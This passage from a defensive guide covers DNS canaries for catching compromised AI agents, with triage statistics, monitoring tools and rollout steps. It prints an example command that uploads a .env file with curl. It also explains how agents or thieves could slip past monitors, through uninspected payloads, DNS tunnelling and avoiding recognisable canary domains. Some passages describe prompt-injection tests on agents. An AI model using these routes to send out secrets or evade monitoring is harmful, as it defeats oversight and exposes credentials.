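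The defender has no local log to fall back on when an alert from a thief's own machine is lost. Snare, a tool that plants decoy credentials, sends its alert as a web request, which can be lost in the same way as a DNS lookup. In *There's an AWS feature nobody uses for detection. I fixed that*, Trevor explains that if a firewall blocks the request or the machine is offline, the thief still gets the fake credentials but the defender gets no alert. Trevor recommends a callback server inside the defender's network, where the defender can monitor outages. That server covers the defender's own agents, but a thief elsewhere can't reach it, so a DNS canary that has to detect use after a theft needs a server on the public internet.

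### Names that the thief avoids

The thief may also recognise the canary and never look it up. No query is then sent, so neither a lower TTL nor a better log would help. Trevor acknowledges that Snare's callback domain became a recognisable sign of a canary once the project was public, and says that a widely used security tool already identifies some hosted decoy keys by their format, without using them.

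An attacker can skip every name under a public canary service's domain and lose nothing. Defenders can address this by using their own domain, preferably one that already appears in real settings. If a company uses its own example.com, an attacker who skips every name under it would also miss the company's real servers.

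## Lookups that do not mean theft

A lookup that reaches the canary server may come from a link scanner, a curious colleague or an honest agent. In *Honeypots for AI Agents*, obormot writes that a fake host has no legitimate use, so the false alarm rate is near zero. That is a fair claim about people logging in to a fake server, but a DNS lookup is much easier to trigger, because a lot of software looks up hostnames only to inspect or test them.

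### Who else looks up a planted name

| Who or what makes the lookup | Why | What can give it away |
|---|---|---|
| Mail or link scanner | It opens links in a message to check for malware | Someone sent the text just before the lookup |
| Chat service | It builds a preview of a posted link | Someone posted the link just before the lookup |
| Malware sandbox | It opens a suspicious document and runs its macros | A security product uploaded the document |
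| Secret scanner | It tests whether a key or connection string works | Someone has just committed the file to a repository |
| Search indexer | It follows links while crawling a wiki or file share | Several planted links cause alerts during one crawl |
| Agent platform | It may check a link before the agent opens it | The agent's session contains the link |
| Colleague | Curiosity, or a mistake | The lookup comes from the office, and the colleague can explain it |
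| Honest agent | It tries the host as part of its task | The session log contains the command |

Links cause most false alarms, because many mail providers and security tools automatically fetch every link in a message. Buttondown's *canary links*, a help page from a newsletter service, lists the problems that arise when a sender mistakes these visits for human ones: inflated click counts, accidental unsubscribes, and sign-ups confirmed by a machine. Chat previews can also trigger a canary link without a click, as Null Byte's *How to Track a Target Using Canary Token Tracking Links* notes. An engineer who pastes a planted link into the team chat to ask what it is may therefore trigger the canary.

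Security products also open files and try out keys. GitHub's secret scanner triggers credential canaries because it tests whether the AWS and Slack keys it finds are active, as Thinkst Canary's *Why am I seeing this note?* explains. A scanner that tested database connection strings would trigger a DNS canary, because it would have to look up the host. A second Thinkst Canary note with the same title covers WildFire, Palo Alto Networks' malware analysis service. WildFire opens Word and Excel files that contain macros and runs the macros, including any that contain a canary.

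An honest agent can cause an alert less predictably. As obormot points out, an agent with a developer's permissions may collect credential files while gathering context, or decide that a credential it has found is relevant to its task. Only the second can trigger a DNS canary. Developers on shared machines may also mistake a planted credential for a real one and use it for work, so obormot prefers environments that only agents use. An alert from an honest agent still has some value because it shows that the agent tries hosts nobody told it to contact.

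### The Log4Shell scans

In December 2021, many security teams used DNS callbacks to search for Log4Shell, a flaw in the Java logging library Log4j. When a vulnerable version logged text containing a certain kind of expression, it contacted the host named in that expression. A tester could put an expression with a unique hostname into a web form or a request header and wait for a DNS lookup of that hostname.

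A lookup did not always mean that the tested application was vulnerable. The application might have passed the text to a vulnerable log collector elsewhere in the company. A security filter might have looked up the hostname in the request to check its reputation, without running Log4j. Even a lookup by the tested application itself did not prove that an attacker could run code there, because a firewall might have blocked the connection that the attack needed.

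Some testers ruled out some of these false alarms by adding `${hostName}` to the front of the planted hostname. Log4j replaced this expression with the name of the machine it was running on, then looked up the result. A query that began with a machine name, such as `build-07`, showed that Log4j had processed the text on that machine. A filter that merely copied the hostname could not fill in the machine name. Similarly, a decoy script that adds its machine's name to a canary shows the defender that the script ran and on which machine, but a plain hostname in a configuration file provides no such evidence.

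### How strangers learn a planted name

Public certificate logs can expose a planted name. The authorities that issue certificates for encrypted web connections record them in these logs so that domain owners can spot certificates they never requested. Anyone can read the logs and look up each new name. If the defender gets a certificate for a decoy web server under a planted name, strangers may query that name within minutes, even though no thief has accessed the file that contains it.

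A wildcard certificate for `*.int.example.com` reveals only the zone. But the asterisk matches only one label, so the certificate works for `q4mz81vtk7c0x5hy.int.example.com` but not for `orders-ro.q4mz81vtk7c0x5hy.int.example.com`.

Registering a new domain for canaries can also attract attention. *DarkDNS*, a study in the programme of the 2024 Internet Measurement Conference, released a live public feed of newly registered domains (SIGCOMM, 2024). People who follow such a feed learn the domain but not the labels under it. Their queries for common names like "www" should go in the daily summary of unknown labels rather than raise alerts.

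Passive DNS databases hold names and answers that companies have collected from DNS traffic, and customers can search them. Once somebody has looked up a planted name, it can enter such a database, and anyone who searches for names under int.example.com may then find it and look it up again.

In *Watching the Watchers*, Roberts and Plonka (2020) measured how far unique values travel. In 2019 they sent more than a billion packets, each with a different source address from a previously unused block, and recorded about 247,000 reactions to those addresses, roughly one for every 4,700 packets. Most were reverse lookups, which find the name that belongs to an address. Most reactions came within 24 hours, but one reverse lookup came 113 days later. In 175 cases, a commercial passive DNS database had recorded a lookup of the address, so somebody was sharing this traffic with a third party.

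These rates don't apply directly to planted hostnames, because every network along the route can see a packet's source address, while outsiders can't see a hostname in a file until someone sends it somewhere or looks it up.

### Queries that come back

Resolvers and observers may repeat a canary query for months after the first lookup. APNIC, the organisation that allocates internet addresses in the Asia-Pacific region, found such repeats using online advertisements. Each advertisement made the viewer's browser fetch items from unique hostnames that contained the time. The answers had a TTL of one second. In theory, each name should have caused one or two queries within a few seconds.

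Over five and a half months from October 2015, the servers received 44.7 billion queries. APNIC's *DNS Zombies* (2016) reports that about a quarter were for names more than an hour old, and that 1% of all queries were for names more than 83 days old.

For a single canary, the risk is lower than this suggests. About 60% of the late queries were for names that broken resolvers looked up around a million times a day or more. The late queries involved 59 million different names, while the advertisements generated about 24 million new names every day. If both figures are typical of the whole period, only about 1.5% of the names were queried again after an hour.

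Other late queries looked deliberate. One address at Team Cymru, a security company, sent 573 million late queries and only seven timely ones. APNIC suggests that systems like this collect the web addresses that people visit and then check them.

*DNS Query Duplication* (Huston, 2026), a newer study, measured how often queries repeat almost at once. On 1 June 2026, APNIC's servers received queries for about 146 million single-use names, now with a TTL of 60 seconds. Lost packets should have caused repeats for about 2% of the names, but 38% had repeats, counting only queries for the same record type. The figure was 27% in Europe and western Asia and 61% in the Indian subcontinent.

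About 45% of the repeats came within 10 milliseconds of the first query, much too soon for a resolver to have timed out. Of those within the first 100 milliseconds, 82% came from a different address. Huston suggests that some systems query several resolvers at once and use the first answer. Repeats also peaked slightly after 6, 12 and 18 hours, probably because some resolvers were refreshing old entries. So if two addresses query a planted name within the same second, the most likely explanation is a single lookup by a single program.

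Some observers also keep the data they see and use it later. Xing, Lu and colleagues studied this practice, called traffic shadowing, in *Yesterday Once More*. They sent decoy DNS, web and encrypted traffic through 4,364 points rented from commercial VPN providers and recorded requests that the decoys should not have caused. DNS queries to several public resolvers were the most exposed. Observers sometimes kept the data for more than ten days and used it more than once. Many of the unexpected requests came from addresses on blocklists, but most were only reconnaissance, and the researchers saw no attempted attacks. An alert from a blocklisted address is therefore poor evidence of theft.

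The names in these experiments had all been used at least once, so the results can't predict how often an untouched canary will cause a false alarm. They do suggest treating the first lookup very differently from the rest. Something must have exposed the name before that lookup, and the defender should find out what. Later lookups may not come from a person or agent. For example, if the defender tests the planted name itself in September, a resolver may repeat the query in December and cause an alert.

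### Whose address is in the log

In the example row from the canary server's log, 198.51.100.7 is the resolver's address. An investigator can look up its owner and country, but the owner may not be the thief, and the thief may be in another country.

*Who Resolves Your DNS?* (Thiagarajan and Bustamante, 2026) tested how well such an address matches the client's situation. The study used RIPE Atlas, a worldwide network of small measurement devices, mostly on home and company connections. Each device used its normal resolver to look up a name under the researchers' domain. The authoritative server replied with the address from which it had received the query, so the researchers could compare that address with the device's own.

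In October 2025, when a device contacted a resolver at a public address, the authoritative server received the query from a different address in 91.7% of cases. In 18.7% of cases with a known country, the query came from a country other than the device's. One lookup from France used a resolver that appeared to be French but contacted the authoritative server from Finland. About 40% of device-resolver pairs produced queries from several addresses. A lookup from a foreign or new address therefore does not necessarily indicate a thief abroad or a new machine.

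A defender can use the same method to list the addresses from which the company's own lookups normally arrive, by looking up throwaway names several times from every environment where agents run. If a later alert comes from one of these addresses, the company's own machines are the first place to look. A match is weaker evidence when the address belongs to a large public resolver, because people outside the company use it too.

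The company's resolver log can show which machine on its network made a lookup, but it does not record lookups from the thief's machine.

Client-subnet data, the part of the client's address that some resolvers pass on, can sometimes fill part of that gap. The DNS standard for it, RFC 7871, recommends sending no more than the first 24 bits of an IPv4 address, which leaves 256 possible client addresses. For example, an alert might also contain the subnet 203.0.113.0/24. If the company's office uses that block, the lookup most likely came from a colleague or an office machine. If the block belongs to a hosting company that the defender has never used, the name has probably been sent outside the company.

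Many resolvers don't send the client's subnet to the canary server, often to protect privacy. When they do, the subnet may belong to a VPN server or a company gateway shared by thousands of people. Someone who queries the canary server directly can also put any subnet into the query. The subnet is a useful hint about where to search next, but it can't identify a person or an agent.

### How often an alert is genuine

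Even a low rate of harmless lookups can outnumber genuine alerts, because compromises are rare. In a hypothetical example, a company has planted 200 names, and each receives 0.02 harmless lookups a month, or about one every four years. One of the company's agents is compromised every 24 months, and each compromise has a 40% chance of triggering a canary.

| | Calculation for one month | Expected over 24 months |
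|---|---|---|
| False alerts | 200 × 0.02 = 4 | 96 |
| Genuine alerts | 0.4 ÷ 24 ≈ 0.017 | 0.4 |

Each alert has about a 0.4% chance (0.4 ÷ 96.4) of being genuine. A team that thoroughly investigated every alert would look into 96 false ones over two years and still have a 60% chance of missing the compromise.

If the company adds a filter that removes 95% of the false alerts and keeps 90% of the genuine ones, it can expect 4.8 false alerts and 0.36 genuine ones over 24 months. An alert that passes the filter then has a 7% chance of being genuine. That is about 17 times the chance without the filter, but about 13 out of 14 alerts are still false.

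It is easier to see the effect of further checks in odds:

odds after a check = odds before × (share of genuine alerts that pass ÷ share of false alerts that pass)

The odds that an alert is genuine start at 0.4 to 96, or 1 to 240. The filter multiplies them by 0.90 ÷ 0.05 = 18. A second check that performed equally well would multiply them by 18 again, giving 324 to 240, or a 57% chance. A third would raise the chance to 96%.

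Each check also rejects a tenth of the genuine alerts, so applying three in a row keeps only 73% of them. The multiplication assumes that the checks fail independently. If one check shows that an address belongs to a foreign hosting company and another finds it on a list of foreign hosting companies, the two count as only one check.

Putting the canaries where they receive fewer harmless lookups works as well as the filter. If each name received 0.001 harmless lookups a month instead of 0.02, the company would have 4.8 false alerts in 24 months without filtering out any genuine ones, and 7.7% of alerts would be genuine. This is a strong reason to put canaries in connection strings rather than links.

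A defender can estimate the actual rate of false alarms from past alerts, but should count each type of location separately. Suppose 100 canaries in environment files have had no lookups in 24 months, for a total of 2,400 months of observation. Dividing three by this total, a common statistical rule, gives an upper limit of 0.00125 lookups per name per month at 95% confidence. A single canary with no lookups over the same 24 months would give a limit of 3 ÷ 24 = 0.125, which is too high to be useful.

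False alerts also change how people treat true ones. In *Honeytoken alerts FP*, a discussion on Microsoft's forum, a user says that honeytoken alerts used to be accurate in every penetration test his company ran. He called the feature useless once routine queries began to set them off. Someone replied, promising to split the alerts by type so that customers could turn off those caused by queries.

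### Triage rules

The odds suggest that a lone DNS alert justifies a few minutes of checking but not an emergency shutdown, and that two independent pieces of supporting evidence justify treating it as a probable compromise. The checks below start with the easiest.

The register records which file contains the name, and the file's owner can say whether anyone has recently moved, emailed, committed or indexed it. A lookup ten seconds after someone emailed the file probably came from a scanner. But the timing doesn't prove this, because a thief could have taken the file weeks earlier and triggered the lookup then by coincidence.

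If the company's own resolver log contains a query for the canary name at about the same time, the entry identifies the machine that made the lookup, or at least narrows the search. If there is no such query, the lookup probably came from outside the company, unless a local cache answered it or the agent used another resolver. If the name existed only in a private file, an outside lookup means that the name must have left the company somehow, and this needs an explanation.

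If the lookup came from an agent's machine, the session log may contain the command that caused it. The defender should then check whether the agent's task explains that command. For example, an agent had some reason to try the database if it was fixing a database test, but not if it was summarising a web page. If the lookup came from outside, the defender should search for every session that has read the file since the name was planted, because the theft may have happened long before the alert.

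If the planted name leads to an address that the defender controls, a connection soon after the lookup is good supporting evidence of theft. In APNIC's measurements from 2015 and 2016, only 0.08% of web fetches were for names more than an hour old, compared with 25% of DNS queries, so a delayed connection is much less likely than a delayed lookup to be an echo. Some scanners also connect, but a connection reveals more about them than a lookup does. Trend Micro's *What is a sandbox?*, a guide for companies that send their staff fake phishing emails, lists obsolete browsers and unusual combinations of browser and operating system as signs of an automated visit. A DNS query doesn't include the browser or operating system. A login attempt with the planted password is even stronger evidence.

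A lookup with no connection after it doesn't rule out theft. A sandbox may have blocked the connection, as happened in BeyondTrust's test, or the thief may have become suspicious after looking up the name.

Lookups of two different canary names are better evidence of theft than two lookups of the same name. In the invented example, four unrelated false alerts a month would produce two within the same hour only about once every four years. But many false alerts are related. An indexer that crawls a wiki can trigger every planted link on it in a few minutes. A second canary is the strongest evidence when it is in a different kind of file from the first, or when it is a credential canary from the same decoy entry.

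Buttondown detects scanners by putting a tiny invisible link in its emails. People don't see the link, so whatever follows it is probably a machine checking every link. A defender could likewise hide a control link on a wiki page beside the planted one. If both names trigger alerts within seconds, a scanner or indexer is the likely cause. This test is less reliable where agents read the page, because an agent working from the page's source code can also see the invisible link, and a compromised one may follow every link it finds.

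Defenders should keep a record of alerts that fail these checks. In the example, the filter rejects one genuine alert in ten, and a thief who looks up one hostname today may try a stolen key next week. Defenders would then know from the earlier alert which file to suspect and roughly when someone first used it.

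## Adding DNS canaries to existing token monitoring

A single DNS alert needs supporting evidence, which operators can often get from tools they already run. Several products monitor AI agents using string canaries, credential canaries or decoy tools, but almost all claims about how well these products work come from their makers.

### What current monitors can see

grith is a program that checks an agent's actions before they run and gives each a risk score. According to grith's *Canary tokens*, part of its documentation, a match with a planted string scores 9.5, and grith blocks anything above 8 without asking the user. It searches only certain parts of certain actions:

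| Action | Text that grith searches for canaries |
|---|---|
| Web request | Method and URL |
| Network connection | Address and port |
| Shell command or new program | The command and its arguments |
| File write | The file's path |
| File read | Nothing |

An agent can therefore read or upload a decoy file without triggering a match. For example, the command `curl --data @.env https://files.example.net` contains the file's name but none of its planted text, and grith says it does not inspect payloads.

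grith's *Setting up canary tokens* seems to contradict this. In its sample dry run, the planted string is in the body of a web request to GitHub, and grith blocks the request even though it treats GitHub as a trusted destination. Perhaps grith can search a body that the agent writes into the call itself, but not one that a program reads from a file. An operator should test both cases.

In grith version 0.3.1, canaries added with `grith canary add` never reach the running program, so the operator has to list them in a configuration file and restart grith. Matches go into the general audit log because there is no separate canary alert.

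A search for exact text can also miss encoded secrets. *Caught in the Act(ivation)* compared detectors on test prompts for a small open-weight model. Simple text search had an AUROC of 0.73, on a scale where 0.5 is guessing and 1 is perfect. A detector that examined the model's internal activity scored 0.998, but it needs access to that activity. The researchers call their results preliminary.

Snare alerts when somebody tries to use a decoy credential. Snare's *Credential-use tripwires for AI agents* lists 18 types of decoy, and the default installation plants three, for AWS, SSH and Kubernetes. An AWS profile can run a command to obtain its key, and the command in Snare's decoy profile sends a web request to a callback server before returning a fake key. Trevor, who wrote Snare, claims that the alert goes out about 0.01 seconds after the agent starts its AWS command, compared with an average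 of two to three minutes for decoy keys monitored through CloudTrail, AWS's audit log.

The callback happens only if the planted command runs, so a thief who copies the fake key out of it and tries the key directly with AWS triggers no alert. Some other decoys have side effects. For example, the one for Python packages makes every package installation on the machine contact Snare's server, and false alarms are frequent, according to Snare.

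Tracebit's *Detecting CI/CD supply chain attacks with canary credentials* describes an add-on for GitHub's build service, which compiles and tests software automatically. The add-on gives each run decoy AWS credentials and SSH keys. Tracebit tags these with the repository, workflow, job, code version and run ID, so each alert can be traced to a single run. Its promise of "no false positives" is too strong, because an uncompromised agent may also try a key it finds.

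Tracebit (2026) also offers instructions and scripts for the AI agent OpenClaw that plant five types of decoy. The agent checks the user's inbox for alert emails about every 30 minutes and investigates any it finds. This relies on a possibly compromised agent to report on itself, so a person should receive the emails too. Tracebit says its canaries caught all three injection attempts in a 48-hour experiment, while standard defenses caught none. Three attempts are too few to estimate a detection rate.

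Thinkst's decoy MCP server can alert when an agent connects and fetches the list of tools, or when it calls one. Thinkst recommends alerting on connections in environments where nobody uses MCP, and only on tool calls where agents already use it. The alert contains the client's public address, the MCP method and the name of any tool called.

Thinkst's *Getting Agents to tell on themselves* (September 2026) introduced a decoy web service that offers to help agents exploring a network and asks them about their plans. Thinkst says agents fell for it every time in its internal tests, but had not yet published a description of the test networks. One agent answered with an invented SSH key, so defenders should check anything an agent tells the service.

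### Grafana's decoy key

On 26 April 2025, an attacker used a vulnerable GitHub workflow at Grafana Labs, a maker of monitoring software, to steal secrets. Grafana Labs' *Canary tokens* (2025) explains that the company had planted decoy AWS keys among those secrets. The attacker ran TruffleHog, an open-source program that finds secrets and tests whether they work. TruffleHog sent AWS a request to identify the owner of a decoy key, which triggered an alert in the company's Slack.

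Grafana had planted some keys for the whole organisation and others for single repositories. The organisation-wide keys can reveal a theft from any repository, and the single-repository keys show which one the thief got into. Grafana says the alert revealed the entry point and that its teams contained the intrusion within minutes. It found no changes to its code and no access to production systems.

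This incident is good evidence for credential canaries, because a real thief tested stolen keys and a decoy among them exposed the theft. Grafana also plants DNS tokens in unused subdomains, but it does not say they helped detect this theft, so the incident is not evidence for DNS canaries.

The kind of key also mattered. Grafana used Thinkst's paid service, and says TruffleHog recognises the free service's keys without contacting AWS.

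### What a DNS canary adds

Haryati and Zychlinski recommend both credential canaries and resolver-log matching, but neither detects a thief trying a stolen database address from another machine. The database supposedly belongs to the company, so no cloud provider can report the attempt, and the lookup goes through the thief's own resolver, so it doesn't appear in the company's logs.

A DNS canary covers this case, whereas grith can't monitor the thief's machine and a decoy AWS key reveals only attempts to use that key. The defender also doesn't need an account with a cloud provider. Weinberg points out that decoys in general can reveal an attacker's infrastructure when used after a theft, even if nobody noticed the break-in. A DNS canary may reveal only a resolver's address.

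A DNS canary also has an advantage over Snare's AWS callback in a sandbox that allows DNS but blocks web traffic. The callback's address is snare.sh/c/ followed by the decoy's identifier, so a DNS query would contain only snare.sh, which many users share. A DNS canary has the identifier in its hostname, so the query includes it.

A DNS canary adds less if a company already has decoy cloud keys in every file that matters. It helps only when an agent or thief tries the hosts in a stolen file before trying the decoy keys, or without trying the keys at all.

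### One hostname as two canaries

The same hostname can also serve as a string canary. To do this in grith, the operator adds the random label from the decoy database address to grith's list:

```toml
[[canary.tokens]]
id = "c1f0a6de-2b57-4f0e-8a41-6d3f9b7e2c10"
label = "build-07 REPORTS_DB_URL"
value = "q4mz81vtk7c0x5hy"
```

It is better to list only the random label than the whole hostname, because the match then still works if the agent drops "orders-ro" or the domain. The two canaries react to different events:

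| What happens | String canary in grith | DNS canary |
|---|---|---|
| The agent reads the file | No match | No lookup |
| The agent runs a command containing the hostname | Match, and grith blocks the command | No lookup, because the command never runs |
| The agent runs a script that loads the setting and connects | Probably no match | Alert, if the lookup gets out |
| The agent uploads the file with a command that contains only the file's name | No match | No lookup yet |
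| The thief tries the address on another machine | grith can't see it | Alert |

The string canary probably doesn't detect the script because the command contains only the script's name, and the program then usually connects to a numerical address. In the second row, the canary server receives no query if grith blocks the command, so the lack of a query doesn't make grith's match less credible during triage.

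A match in grith does not always mean theft either, although grith's documentation calls a canary in an outbound call "proof that something is exfiltrating". grith searches all shell commands, so an uncompromised agent that runs `grep q4mz81vtk7c0x5hy .env` to find the setting would trigger a match without sending any data.

The list of canaries also needs protection. grith looks for its configuration file relative to the directory where it started. If the operator starts it in the project's folder, the agent may be able to read the list.

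An agent that encodes the file and sends it through a DNS tunnel can get past both canaries, so resolver-log matching is still useful.

### Plans for built-in DNS canaries

As of October 2026, no agent-monitoring project appears to have documented plans for DNS canaries. The closest product is already on sale. DecoyOps' *The attack chain has evolved* advertises bait files whose hidden instructions trigger a DNS canary when an AI agent processes them. By the seller's description, this detects that an agent has read the file and acted on the text, but an honest agent might do that too.

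Other projects have different priorities. Waldrep develops Pipelock, an open-source program that inspects agents' traffic. In *The v0.2 roadmap for Pipelock*, Waldrep announced a GitHub add-on, checks on what agents send to MCP tools, and better rules against data loss. Help Net Security's *Pipelock* reports later plans for signed records of agents' activity that outside auditors can verify. Haryati and Zychlinski propose a DNS traffic detector designed for agents and a standard test of what can leave a sandbox.

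SamsonCyber's *Agent Canary* offers decoy files, tools, web addresses and environment variables, but no DNS canary. *mcpbait*, a program for testing whether a malicious tool server can hijack an agent, is advertised as not needing a DNS canary. It acts as the malicious server itself, so any leaked decoy appears in its own log. Snare lists DNS among the strengths of Canarytokens and recommends using both products.

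An operator who wants to use DNS canaries with these tools therefore has to connect the two, as Kadam did when he combined Thinkst's DNS tokens with decoy tools.

### Rolling it out in stages

#### Choose the routes and plant a few names

The operator should first list the routes that existing monitors miss. For example, if a company runs grith on its developers' machines and plants Tracebit's keys in its builds, three gaps remain: scripts that load a database address from a file, hosted sandboxes where the company can't install grith, and thieves who try stolen addresses elsewhere. Planting a link in a wiki wouldn't cover any of these gaps.

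Five names are enough to start with. grith suggests three to five decoys, each in a different kind of place. Grafana Labs also recommends starting small in high-risk areas, although it now has tens of thousands of decoys.

The operator also has to decide whom to tell about the tokens. Before Grafana announced its tokens, several employees triggered them while looking around. Grafana now suggests posting common token names and locations on the company wiki. This is risky if agents can read the wiki, because a compromised agent could use the page to avoid the tokens listed there. Telling the owners of the affected files directly is safer.

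#### Record without paging anyone

For the first month, alerts should go to a log rather than to anyone's phone, because a public canary server receives stray traffic even when nobody has found a planted name. According to the README for *knary*, several DNS requests for ordinary subdomains arrive every day, and some systems keep sending requests long after a security test has ended. The operator can configure knary to filter out such requests by name or address.

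Someone should still read the log every working day, since a real theft can happen during the trial. A login attempt with a planted password should page someone from the start.

A month without alerts is weak evidence that false alarms are rare. Monitoring five names for one month gives five name-months, so the upper limit on the false alarm rate is about 3 ÷ 5 = 0.6 per name per month. The trial can reveal a start-up script that tests every address each morning, but not a scanner that runs twice a year.

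#### Run test lookups from each environment

A test should take the same path an agent's lookup would. The operator uses the agent's shell tool to look up a throwaway name, such as t4k8w2zq9m.int.example.com, then checks that the query reached the canary server and that a person received the alert. If a filter is supposed to refuse the name, the alert should come from the local log.

The operator should judge the result from the logs, which were correct in two trials where the agent's screen was wrong. In one, Haryati and Zychlinski's resolver refused the stolen data, but the model's command still reported that it had sent everything, because the lookup program treats any DNS reply as a success. In the other, the data arrived but the success message never appeared.

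grith's dry run, `grith proxy test`, checks the string canary but sends nothing, so it can't replace a DNS test. A fuller test is to see whether the agent obeys an attacker. In Dreadnode's *Honeytoken Probing (RCE & Data Exfil)*, the tester gives the agent a malicious instruction and a unique but harmless marker. The software then looks for the marker in the agent's output, its tool calls and the log of a collecting server, including copies in base64 or hexadecimal. It keeps the assessment open until the tester has removed every marker.

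#### Connect alerts to agent sessions

An alert is much more useful if the operator can find the session behind it. Levine, Lejeail and Mooney, in *What we learned about AI agent security by monitoring our agents*, report that ordinary application logs may include an agent's last call but not the prompt or retrieved text that led to it. The session record therefore has to include what the agent read as well as what it ran. With such a record, the operator could reconstruct the example alert like this:

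| Time | Log | Entry |
|---|---|---|
| 14:02:57 | Session | Session 5831 reads a README from an outside repository |
| 14:03:20 | Session | Session 5831 runs `python check_db.py` |
| 14:03:22 | Agent's resolver | build-07 looks up the planted name |
| 14:03:22 | Canary server | A query for the planted name arrives |

This works only if the machines' clocks agree. If several agents share build-07, the time and machine may match more than one session. One remedy, suggested by Tracebit's tags, is to create a new label for each session and store the session's ID in the register.

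Some tools can already write such records. SANS Internet Storm Center describes numbat, which attaches to coding agents such as Claude and starts in a monitoring-only mode. By default, it saves events to a file in the user's home directory. An agent running under the same account may be able to change that file, so another system should collect copies as the agent works.

#### Enable automatic responses

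The first automatic response should be reversible and cause little disruption. Decoy, a product with decoy tools, is advertised as pausing an agent for ten minutes after it calls one. In the earlier invented example with four false alerts a month, similar pauses would take up at most 40 minutes of agent time a month, which is acceptable even though very few of the alerts would be genuine.

The software can pause the right agent only if the local log identifies its session. A lookup from an unknown resolver doesn't identify an agent to pause. Replacing passwords can interrupt real services, so a person should decide whether to do it.

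### What to do when an alert arrives

1. **Preserve the logs.** Copy the records from the canary server, the resolver, the web proxy and the agent's session to a place the agent can't reach. The attacker at Grafana deleted the copied repository, the proposed changes and the workflow runs used in the attack. Some systems also delete old logs automatically within days.

2. **Suspend the session.** Pause the agent and cut off its network access, including DNS, but keep its files and memory for investigation. Check that it has really stopped, because the automatic stop failed in OpenAI's September incident. If the lookup came from outside, suspend any running session that has read the planted file.

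3. **Identify the placement.** Look up the label in the register, then check for copies of the file in backups, container images and other repositories. The suspected agent should not take part, since an attacker may control its answers.

4. **Rotate nearby real secrets.** Once a second piece of evidence supports the alert, replace every real key and password in the same file, then any others that the session could read. As Snare's *Canary Tokens for the Agentic Era* notes, malware that steals a file takes the real keys along with the decoy. Disable the old secrets as well as issuing new ones, and work from a machine the agent hasn't used.

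5. **Replace the name.** Plant a new decoy with a new label, but keep watching the old one. Grafana archives used tokens because an attacker may try them again or sell them.

Grafana advises acknowledging alerts promptly in Thinkst's console, because the console otherwise groups later alerts with the first. A second lookup from a different address, perhaps by somebody who bought the stolen file, could then go unnoticed.

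Step 4 is easier if there are few long-lived secrets to replace. Haryati and Zychlinski recommend short-lived credentials that a program fetches only when it needs them. A stolen credential may then expire before anyone has finished reading the logs.

### Deciding whether the deployment works

Four measurements show whether the canaries do what the operator expects. The figures in this table are invented:

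| Measure | Calculation | Example |
|---|---|---|
| Coverage | Combinations of environment and route with a successful test ÷ all combinations chosen | 12 ÷ 15 = 80% |
| Delay | Time from the lookup until a person receives the alert | Median 40 seconds, slowest 6 minutes |
| False alerts | Harmless alerts ÷ name-months | 2 ÷ 60 ≈ 0.033 |
| Missed tests | Tests without an alert ÷ all tests | 0 ÷ 30 |

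The number of planted names is a poor measure of coverage, because a company could plant a thousand names in developers' files and none in the hosted sandbox where its agents run code. The operator should also list the three failed combinations, because one of them may be the environment with the most valuable secrets. Even 100% coverage doesn't show whether a thief will try the name.

Alert delay should be measured up to the moment a person sees the alert. If an agent checks an inbox every 30 minutes, an email waits 15 minutes on average and up to 30. Trevor estimates that a compromised agent can find credentials, try them and move on in less than ten seconds. Only an automatic pause has a chance of interrupting an agent that fast, but a slower alert can still limit how long a thief has to use stolen passwords.

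In the example, 20 names caused two false alerts in three months. Two alerts are too few to estimate the rate precisely, and at 95% confidence it could be as high as 0.1 per name per month. At that rate, 200 names would cause 20 false alerts a month, so the operator should add names gradually.

**Missed tests.** Thirty tests without a miss look convincing but leave room for many failures. If the true miss rate is p, the chance of 30 successes in a row is (1 − p)³⁰. This equals 5% when p is about 0.095, so at 95% confidence the miss rate could still be almost 10%. Larger numbers of tests give tighter limits:

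| Tests without a miss | Highest miss rate still plausible at 95% confidence |
|---|---|
| 10 | 26% |
| 30 | 10% |
| 59 | 5% |
| 299 | 1% |

One miss in 30 tests raises the limit to about 15%. The operator should find the cause of any miss before running more tests, since a single firewall rule may block every lookup from that environment.

The calculation assumes that the tests are independent and equally likely to fail. Thirty lookups from one machine in one minute mostly repeat the same test. If the company spreads its 30 tests evenly over three environments, each gets only ten, and the limit for each is 26%. At one test a week, each environment would take more than a year to reach 59. The count should start again whenever someone changes the sandbox, the resolver or the alerting.
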